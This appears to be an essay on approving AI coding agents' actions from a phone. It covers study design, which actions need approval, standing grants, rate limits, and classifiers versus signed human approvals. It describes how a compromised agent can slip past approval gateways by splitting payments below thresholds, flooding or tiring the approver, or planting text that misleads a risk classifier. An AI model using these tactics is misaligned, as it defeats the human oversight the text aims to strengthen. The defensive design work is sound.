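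The developers would do their normal work for four weeks. If each received about ten requests per working day, or 200 in total, the researchers would plant four harmful ones among each developer's requests, such as a push that removes a colleague's commits or an email with an extra recipient. That is one request in 50, compared with one in two in the studies by Hossain and Jubur. The gateway would block the planted requests even if a developer approved them. The developers would agree beforehand to occasional tests without knowing when to expect them. They would get their results only at the end, because learning immediately that they had approved a harmful request would probably make them more careful for a while and change what the experiment was measuring.

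Half of the planted requests should contain a visible error, such as a wrong recipient. The others should look normal unless the developer remembers or looks up what happened earlier. Using the phone might help developers catch the visible errors but make them miss more of the others, and a single average could hide both effects.

To plan the size of the study, suppose people catch 50% of harmful requests in one group and the researchers want to detect a rise to 65% in another. With the usual 5% threshold for significance and an 80% chance of detecting a real difference, the number of independent decisions in each group is roughly

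`n ≈ (1.96 + 0.84)² × (0.50 × 0.50 + 0.65 × 0.35) / 0.15² ≈ 166`

The 1.96 comes from the significance threshold and the 0.84 from the 80% chance of detection. A slightly more exact formula gives 170. Smaller improvements need far larger studies. For example, detecting a rise from 50% to 55% would take about 1,565 decisions per group.

The four decisions from each developer aren't independent, because a careful person tends to be careful every time. The usual correction multiplies the sample by

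`1 + (m − 1) × ρ`

where *m* is the number of harmful requests per person and ρ measures how similar one person's decisions are. If ρ is 0.2, four requests each give a factor of 1.6. The researchers then need 272 decisions per group, or 68 developers, for a total of 272 people. If ρ is 0.4, they need 94 developers per group. Nobody has published a value of ρ for agent approvals, so a pilot would have to estimate it.

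The table also contains three comparisons, and testing several raises the chance that at least one appears significant by luck. Dividing the 5% threshold by three to correct for this increases the requirement from 170 to about 227 independent decisions per group. With a ρ of 0.2, that requires 91 developers per group, or 364 in all, before allowing for dropouts.

The catch rate alone could be misleading. Suppose the terminal group catches 50% of harmful requests and refuses 5% of harmless ones, while the phone group catches 65% and refuses 20%. Signal detection theory provides a measure of how well people tell the two kinds of request apart:

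`d′ = z(catch rate) − z(false refusal rate)`

Here *z* converts a percentage into a distance on the normal curve. The terminal group scores 1.64 and the phone group 1.23. The phone users have become more willing to refuse, but worse at telling harmful requests from harmless ones. If their false refusal rate had stayed at 5%, they would have scored 2.03, an improvement in judgement.

Researchers should count unanswered requests separately from approvals and refusals. If a developer never sees the notification, a harmful action doesn't run, but she hasn't evaluated it. Counting it as a refusal would give a phone with notifications switched off a perfect catch rate. Researchers should also keep participants in their original groups for the analysis, even those who find a way to turn approvals off. Otherwise, the phone groups would contain only people who didn't mind the interruption.

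A four-week study of several hundred developers would be expensive, but a company that already runs a gateway could do it with its own staff. A shorter study could follow Anthropic's test, in which 1,053 paid testers each received one dangerous command, so their decisions were independent. Splitting that many testers among four ways of asking for approval would give about 263 decisions per group, more than the 227 needed to detect a 15-point difference. This would show whether the phone makes people more careful in a single session, but not whether they would still be more careful after a month, when reaching for the phone would have become routine.

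## Which actions should need a phone approval?

If every request went to the phone, reaching for it would soon become as automatic as pressing a key in the terminal. It would also take time. At 20 seconds each, 40 approvals a day would take about 13 minutes, while 4 would take less than 2 minutes. Twenty seconds is optimistic for a detailed card, since people typically needed 33 seconds for the consequence card designed by Hossain and colleagues. At that rate, 40 approvals would take 22 minutes. These figures exclude the time spent finding the phone and returning to the interrupted work.

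A handful of approval requests a day may be realistic because few of an agent's actions are irreversible. In Anthropic's February 2026 study of agent use, only 0.8% of nearly a million tool calls appeared irreversible. At that rate, an agent that makes 500 calls in a day would make four irreversible ones. The percentage is rough because a language model classified each call in isolation and couldn't always distinguish real actions from simulated ones.

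### Can asking less often be safer?

Kodathala and colleagues simulated ten-task sessions in which each approval request made the approver more likely to accept the next one. Attacks succeeded in 62% of sessions when the gateway required no approvals, 35% when it required approval for everything, and 31% when it required approval only for amounts and new payees.

Asking less improved the last figure only slightly, because 25 of the 31 percentage points came from actions that the policy should have sent for approval but allowed without asking anyone. About 6 points came from attacks that got past the approver, so the simulated approver did much better with fewer requests.

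The researchers assumed a rate at which approvers tire, and the ranking of the policies changed when they varied it. Their 21,840 trials reduce the influence of chance but don't make the assumption more realistic.

Turan (2026), in *Oversight Has a Capacity*, used a simpler fatigue model. The approver makes no mistakes until the number of requests reviewed, ℓ, exceeds a capacity, C. After that, the share of harmful requests the approver catches is

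`r(ℓ) = max(0.2, 1 − 0.02 × (ℓ − C))`

An approver with a capacity of 25 catches 60% of harmful requests after 45 reviews and 20% after 65. Turan applied this model to 125 coding-agent actions chosen to be hard to judge. A language model scored the less obvious ones for risk. When every action went to the approver, 57% of those that needed review or blocking got through. The lowest share that got through was 42%, when 64% of actions went to the approver.

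Turan acknowledges that this result follows from the assumed fatigue. Neither simulation is evidence that real approvers tire at these rates. They do show that a policy can fail by requiring so many approvals that people stop reading the requests, or by not requiring approval for a harmful action.

### What makes an action worth asking about

Irreversibility is the most useful criterion, because a developer can't unsend an email the way they can undo a bad edit. Whether an action is reversible depends on the circumstances as well as the command. For example, `git reset --hard` discards uncommitted changes, but does little harm if there are none. According to Anthropic, Claude Code's automated reviewer therefore receives the repository's current status before it evaluates such a command.

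A team can require approval for payments above a certain amount and for any payment to a new recipient. The new-recipient rule also works for emails and file sharing, where it would catch the hidden copy to an outside address. It wouldn't catch the raw invoice data in Hossain's example, because the user had already approved the auditor as a recipient.

A command that is harmless on a test server can be disastrous on a production server, which customers use. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a design for agents that manage server clusters, sets different rules for each environment. Agents can read data everywhere. They can make changes freely in development, but must notify someone when they make changes in staging (a rehearsal copy of the live system) and get approval before making them in production. They need approval to delete anything in development or staging, and are forbidden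 from deleting anything in production.

Changes to access should need approval even when they are easy to reverse, because an agent can use a new permission before anyone removes it. In one incident at Anthropic, an employee asked Claude to set up read-only access to billing data, and Claude chose a role with full administrative control of the account. An automated reviewer caught the mismatch.

An agent can avoid approval by splitting a large action into small ones, which a limit on the cumulative total can prevent. In one attack tested by Kodathala and colleagues, the agent made ten payments of $50 to a known payee, each below the amount that required approval. The attack always succeeded without a limit on the total and never succeeded with one. By default, ASU requires a fresh approval after five actions or $200 within ten minutes, not counting reads. An agent could still spend nearly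 $1,200 an hour by staying just under $200 in each ten-minute period, so a team should add a daily limit.

Counting doesn't help when steps are harmful only in combination, as in the invoice example. Hossain and colleagues built a monitor that records which files each new file came from and compares an outgoing file's history with the user's instructions. It detected 89.2% of 120 violations. When it could block actions, the share of harmful actions that one agent carried out fell from 43.3% to 5.0%. The monitor can report that it lacks the evidence to judge, which would be a good reason to ask a person.

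The agent shouldn't be able to influence how the gateway applies the approval criteria. AWS recommends fixed rules, because text planted by an attacker could cause a language model to rate a dangerous action as low-risk. The gateway also can't rely on the agent's claim that the user requested something. In Kodathala's tests, an agent made an unwanted change to its stored memory under every approval design, because the policy allowed such changes without approval.

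No list of criteria will suit every team. Turan had a language model play three reviewers, and they agreed only moderately about which actions were risky (a Fleiss' kappa of 0.52, where 0 is chance and 1 is perfect agreement). The "pragmatic" reviewer labelled 87 of the 125 actions safe, while the "cautious" one labelled 45 safe. Human reviewers might agree more or less than these simulated ones, but a team should settle such differences when it writes the policy rather than leave them to whoever holds the phone.

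### A coding agent's day

The table applies these criteria to a developer's agent on an ordinary working day.

| Action | Decision | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Search the project's code | Allow | Changes nothing |
| Edit a source file | Allow | Git can restore the old version |
| Run `npm test` in a sandbox | Allow | The code can't reach credentials or other machines |
| Install a package the project already lists | Allow | The team has already chosen it |
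| Push to the agent's own branch | Allow | Nobody else works there |
| Buy $5 of server time from the usual supplier | Allow, up to a daily total | Small amount, known recipient |
| Force-push to `main` | Ask | Can remove colleagues' commits |
| Delete shared branches | Ask | Someone may still need them |
| Deploy to production | Ask | A mistake affects customers |
| Email a contractor for the first time | Ask | New recipient, and nobody can recall the email |
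| Give the contractor access to the repository | Ask | Lets another person read or change the code |
| Post a file of passwords on a public site | Block | No legitimate task needs it |
| Turn off logging | Block | Hides whatever happens next |
| Change the agent's own permissions | Block | Would defeat the other rules |

Most of the day's activity falls under the first few rows, and the developer gets five approval requests. In Kodathala's tests, ASU's policy averaged 0.75 requests per harmless office or banking task, so ten such tasks would produce seven or eight.

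Blocking an action is better than asking for approval when the answer should always be no, because a tired approver might say yes to a request. If she needs to turn off logging, for example, she can do it herself.

Some systems require confirmation for one important action even when the user has turned off other confirmations. In *PegasusAI Studio* (2026), a platform where agents help scientists run large computations, users can turn off confirmations for routine shell commands but not for submitting a computation. A team could protect forced pushes in the same way, so that a developer who is tired of prompts can't accidentally turn off the prompt for those.

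### Standing grants

A standing grant lets one approval cover later, similar actions. For example, if the agent emails a status report to the same manager every morning, the developer can tick "allow similar" on the first approval card, and the agent can send later reports without asking.

In ASU, the gateway writes the grant, and the agent cannot influence its terms. The grant fixes every argument except those the card explicitly leaves open, which can only be an amount up to a maximum or free text up to a certain length. Recipients, accounts, file paths and web addresses are always fixed. Each grant covers only one tool and one session, has a maximum number of uses and expires. A daily report would therefore need either a long session or a grant that lasts longer than ASU allows.

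These limits don't control what the agent writes in the free text. A grant for status reports could let a compromised agent send confidential information to the manager, though not to anyone else.

Whether grants improve security depends on the approver. In Kodathala's simulation, an agent tried to use a grant for a new recipient. With a fairly attentive approver, the grant option cut the attack's success rate from 20% to 0%, because the gateway compared the recipients itself. With a careless approver, it raised the rate from 30% to 70%.

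Grants should also reduce fatigue, but the researchers' fatigue simulation couldn't test this because none of its tasks repeated a similar action. AWS recommends making the riskiest actions ineligible for grants, or asking people to confirm those grants regularly. It also advises against wildcard grants, which approve all future actions of a type. Claude Code's auto mode ignores rules that allow any Python program because they are close to wildcards.

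### Limits on repeated requests

A compromised agent that gets a refusal can simply ask again, as attackers with a stolen password do with login requests.

ASU's default policy limits this in several ways:

- Each session can have only one card waiting for an answer.
- Identical retries join the existing request instead of creating new cards.
- A session can make at most six calls a minute.
- A user can have at most three pending requests across all sessions.
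- Three refusals lock the requester out.

In the researchers' flooding attack, an agent made up to 30 different harmful requests in one session. The attack always succeeded against the simulated approver without the limits, and still succeeded 45% to 60% of the time with them, depending on the policy.

A simple calculation gives a similar result. If the approver misses each harmful request 20% of the time and the third refusal ends the attack, the chance of at least one approval is

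`1 − 0.8³ ≈ 49%`

Reducing the chance of a mistake on each request to 5% would lower this rate to 14%. A clearer card could therefore help more than a slightly stricter lockout. Locking the agent out after the first refusal would lower the rate to 20% even if the approver made mistakes as often as before, but it would also stop the agent after a harmless misunderstanding.

The per-user cap didn't affect this test because the agent used only one session. It matters when a developer runs several agents, or when one agent opens new sessions to get around the other limits.

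An agent can also wear the approver down with harmless requests before making a harmful one. Turan simulated this attack with an approver whose capacity was 25. When 88% of routine actions needed approval, 50 harmless actions produced about 44 requests, and the harmful action that followed got through 40% of the time. When only 26% needed approval, the attack never succeeded until the agent had taken about 100 harmless actions. In this model, asking for approval less often also makes the attack harder.

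Developers may have to set their own limits on approval requests. Kodathala and colleagues measured request flooding in seven widely used agent runtimes and found that none limited the number of pending requests within a run. In five of them, a single model turn created 20 requests. Microsoft's toolkit allowed 50 and left rate limits to the surrounding software.

### Automated review or a signed approval

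Companies broadly agree that people shouldn't be asked to approve every action. According to *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026), Microsoft told a US government consultation that only higher-impact or uncertain actions should go to human reviewers, while Anthropic and Perplexity described approval fatigue as a core vulnerability. The companies disagree about who should decide on the remaining actions.

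Anthropic's auto mode leaves most approval decisions to software. The agent can read files and edit those inside the project without review. A language-model classifier reviews shell commands, web requests and most other actions. It receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations, which might persuade it to approve an action. A fast check flags suspicious actions, and the classifier then reasons about those in more detail. If it blocks an action, the agent can look for a safer way to do the task.

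The best argument for this approach is Anthropic's test with paid testers, in which the classifier blocked 89% of the dangerous commands while the testers refused 13.6%. The classifier did equally well regardless of session length.

The classifier was less reliable on real mistakes. Anthropic collected 52 cases in which Claude had tried to go beyond what an employee authorized, and an earlier version of the classifier missed 17% of them. With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be between 9% and 30%. The classifier blocked only 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls.

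In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a user who says "Clean up the PR" (a proposed set of code changes) hasn't necessarily agreed to a forced push. A better classifier may not solve this, because the user's message may not show whether they agreed. The user can often answer that with one tap, so there is good reason to keep asking about such actions.

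The coding tool Cursor also uses a classifier. Gomes and McPeak report in *Governing agent autonomy with Auto-review* that it blocks around 4% of the actions it reviews, and that about 7% of chats have at least one interruption. The classifier can open a script before deciding whether the agent may run it, which a person reading a phone screen is unlikely to do. These figures show that the system rarely interrupts people, but they don't measure how many harmful actions it misses.

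Sandboxing makes many approval decisions unnecessary because it limits what a command can reach and therefore damage. But developers have to configure the sandbox for each new capability, and it helps less when a task needs access to the network or the rest of the machine. A sandbox also can't check whether the team wants a particular deployment.

Yubico and IBM argue that people should approve a few consequential actions and that routine work should proceed automatically. In TechRadar's *Why human-in-the-loop authorization is essential for securing AI agents*, a Yubico product manager says the hard problem is proving that a specific person approved an action. Even a perfectly accurate classifier can't provide that proof. If a company's rules require the finance director to authorize large transfers, software that checks a transfer still can't take responsibility for it.

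A signature doesn't improve anyone's judgement. Yubico, which sells security keys, offers no evidence that they help people refuse harmful requests. Anthropic has a commercial interest in agents that work without interruptions.

The two positions are compatible. Anthropic says that auto mode is no replacement for careful human review of high-stakes infrastructure. A team could let a sandbox and a classifier handle routine work, and require a signed approval for the few actions that its policy always sends to a person. The gateway should require that signature even if the classifier approves the action, because otherwise one mistake by the classifier would remove the human check. A classifier could also block obviously harmful requests before they reach the phone, which would spare the approver some prompts.

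### When nobody can answer

Choosing which actions need approval matters more when agents run unattended, because one approval request can stop a night's work. Anthropic's *Running auto mode in production* describes an engineer whose agents compile daily notes from several work tools unsupervised. In his team's analysis, about 10% of session transcripts contained at least one blocked action, so an unattended job needs a plan for what happens after a refusal.

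Auto mode normally returns to manual approval after it blocks three actions in a row or 20 in a session. If Claude Code is running without an interface, nobody can answer, so it stops. For an overnight job, the developer could approve narrow grants before going to bed and have the agent save anything else for the morning. The agent could prepare a forced push, for example, but leave `main` unchanged. In the morning, the gateway should build a new card from the current state of the branch, since colleagues may have added commits overnight.

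Urgent work may need a backup approver. AWS recommends passing unanswered requests to someone else and blocking the action if nobody responds in time. A backup should take over when the main approver is unavailable, not after a refusal. If two people each mistakenly approve 20% of harmful requests, and an agent can ask the second after the first refuses, 36% of harmful requests will be approved.

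Requiring both people to approve stops more harmful requests but also blocks more harmless ones. If their mistakes are independent, only 4% of harmful requests get through. But if each person refuses 5% of harmless requests, nearly 10% of those are now blocked, and every action has to wait for the slower person. Two careless approvers can also still miss most harmful requests. If each catches only 13.6% of them, as Anthropic's testers did, about 75% get through.

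The two approvers' mistakes may not be independent, because the second may assume that the first has read the request. The gateway can reduce this risk by hiding each person's answer until both have responded. *AuthGuard-R* (2026), a design for robots controlled by language models, requires more approvals for riskier actions, so handling hazardous material may need several people. A software team could similarly reserve two-person approval for actions such as deleting a production database.

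A lost phone affects every request until the user enrols another. The company should immediately revoke the old phone's key and cancel any grants made with it. The replacement process must be as secure as the approvals, or an attacker will use it instead. With ASU, an administrator could confirm the person's identity and issue a new one-time enrolment link, as long as the agent can't read the link.

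It is safer to enrol a spare device in advance and keep it somewhere the agent can't reach. Someone who works alone has no administrator or backup approver, so a spare phone or hardware token may be their only quick way to recover access. Until they do, the gateway should keep blocking actions that need approval, and the agent can continue with the rest.
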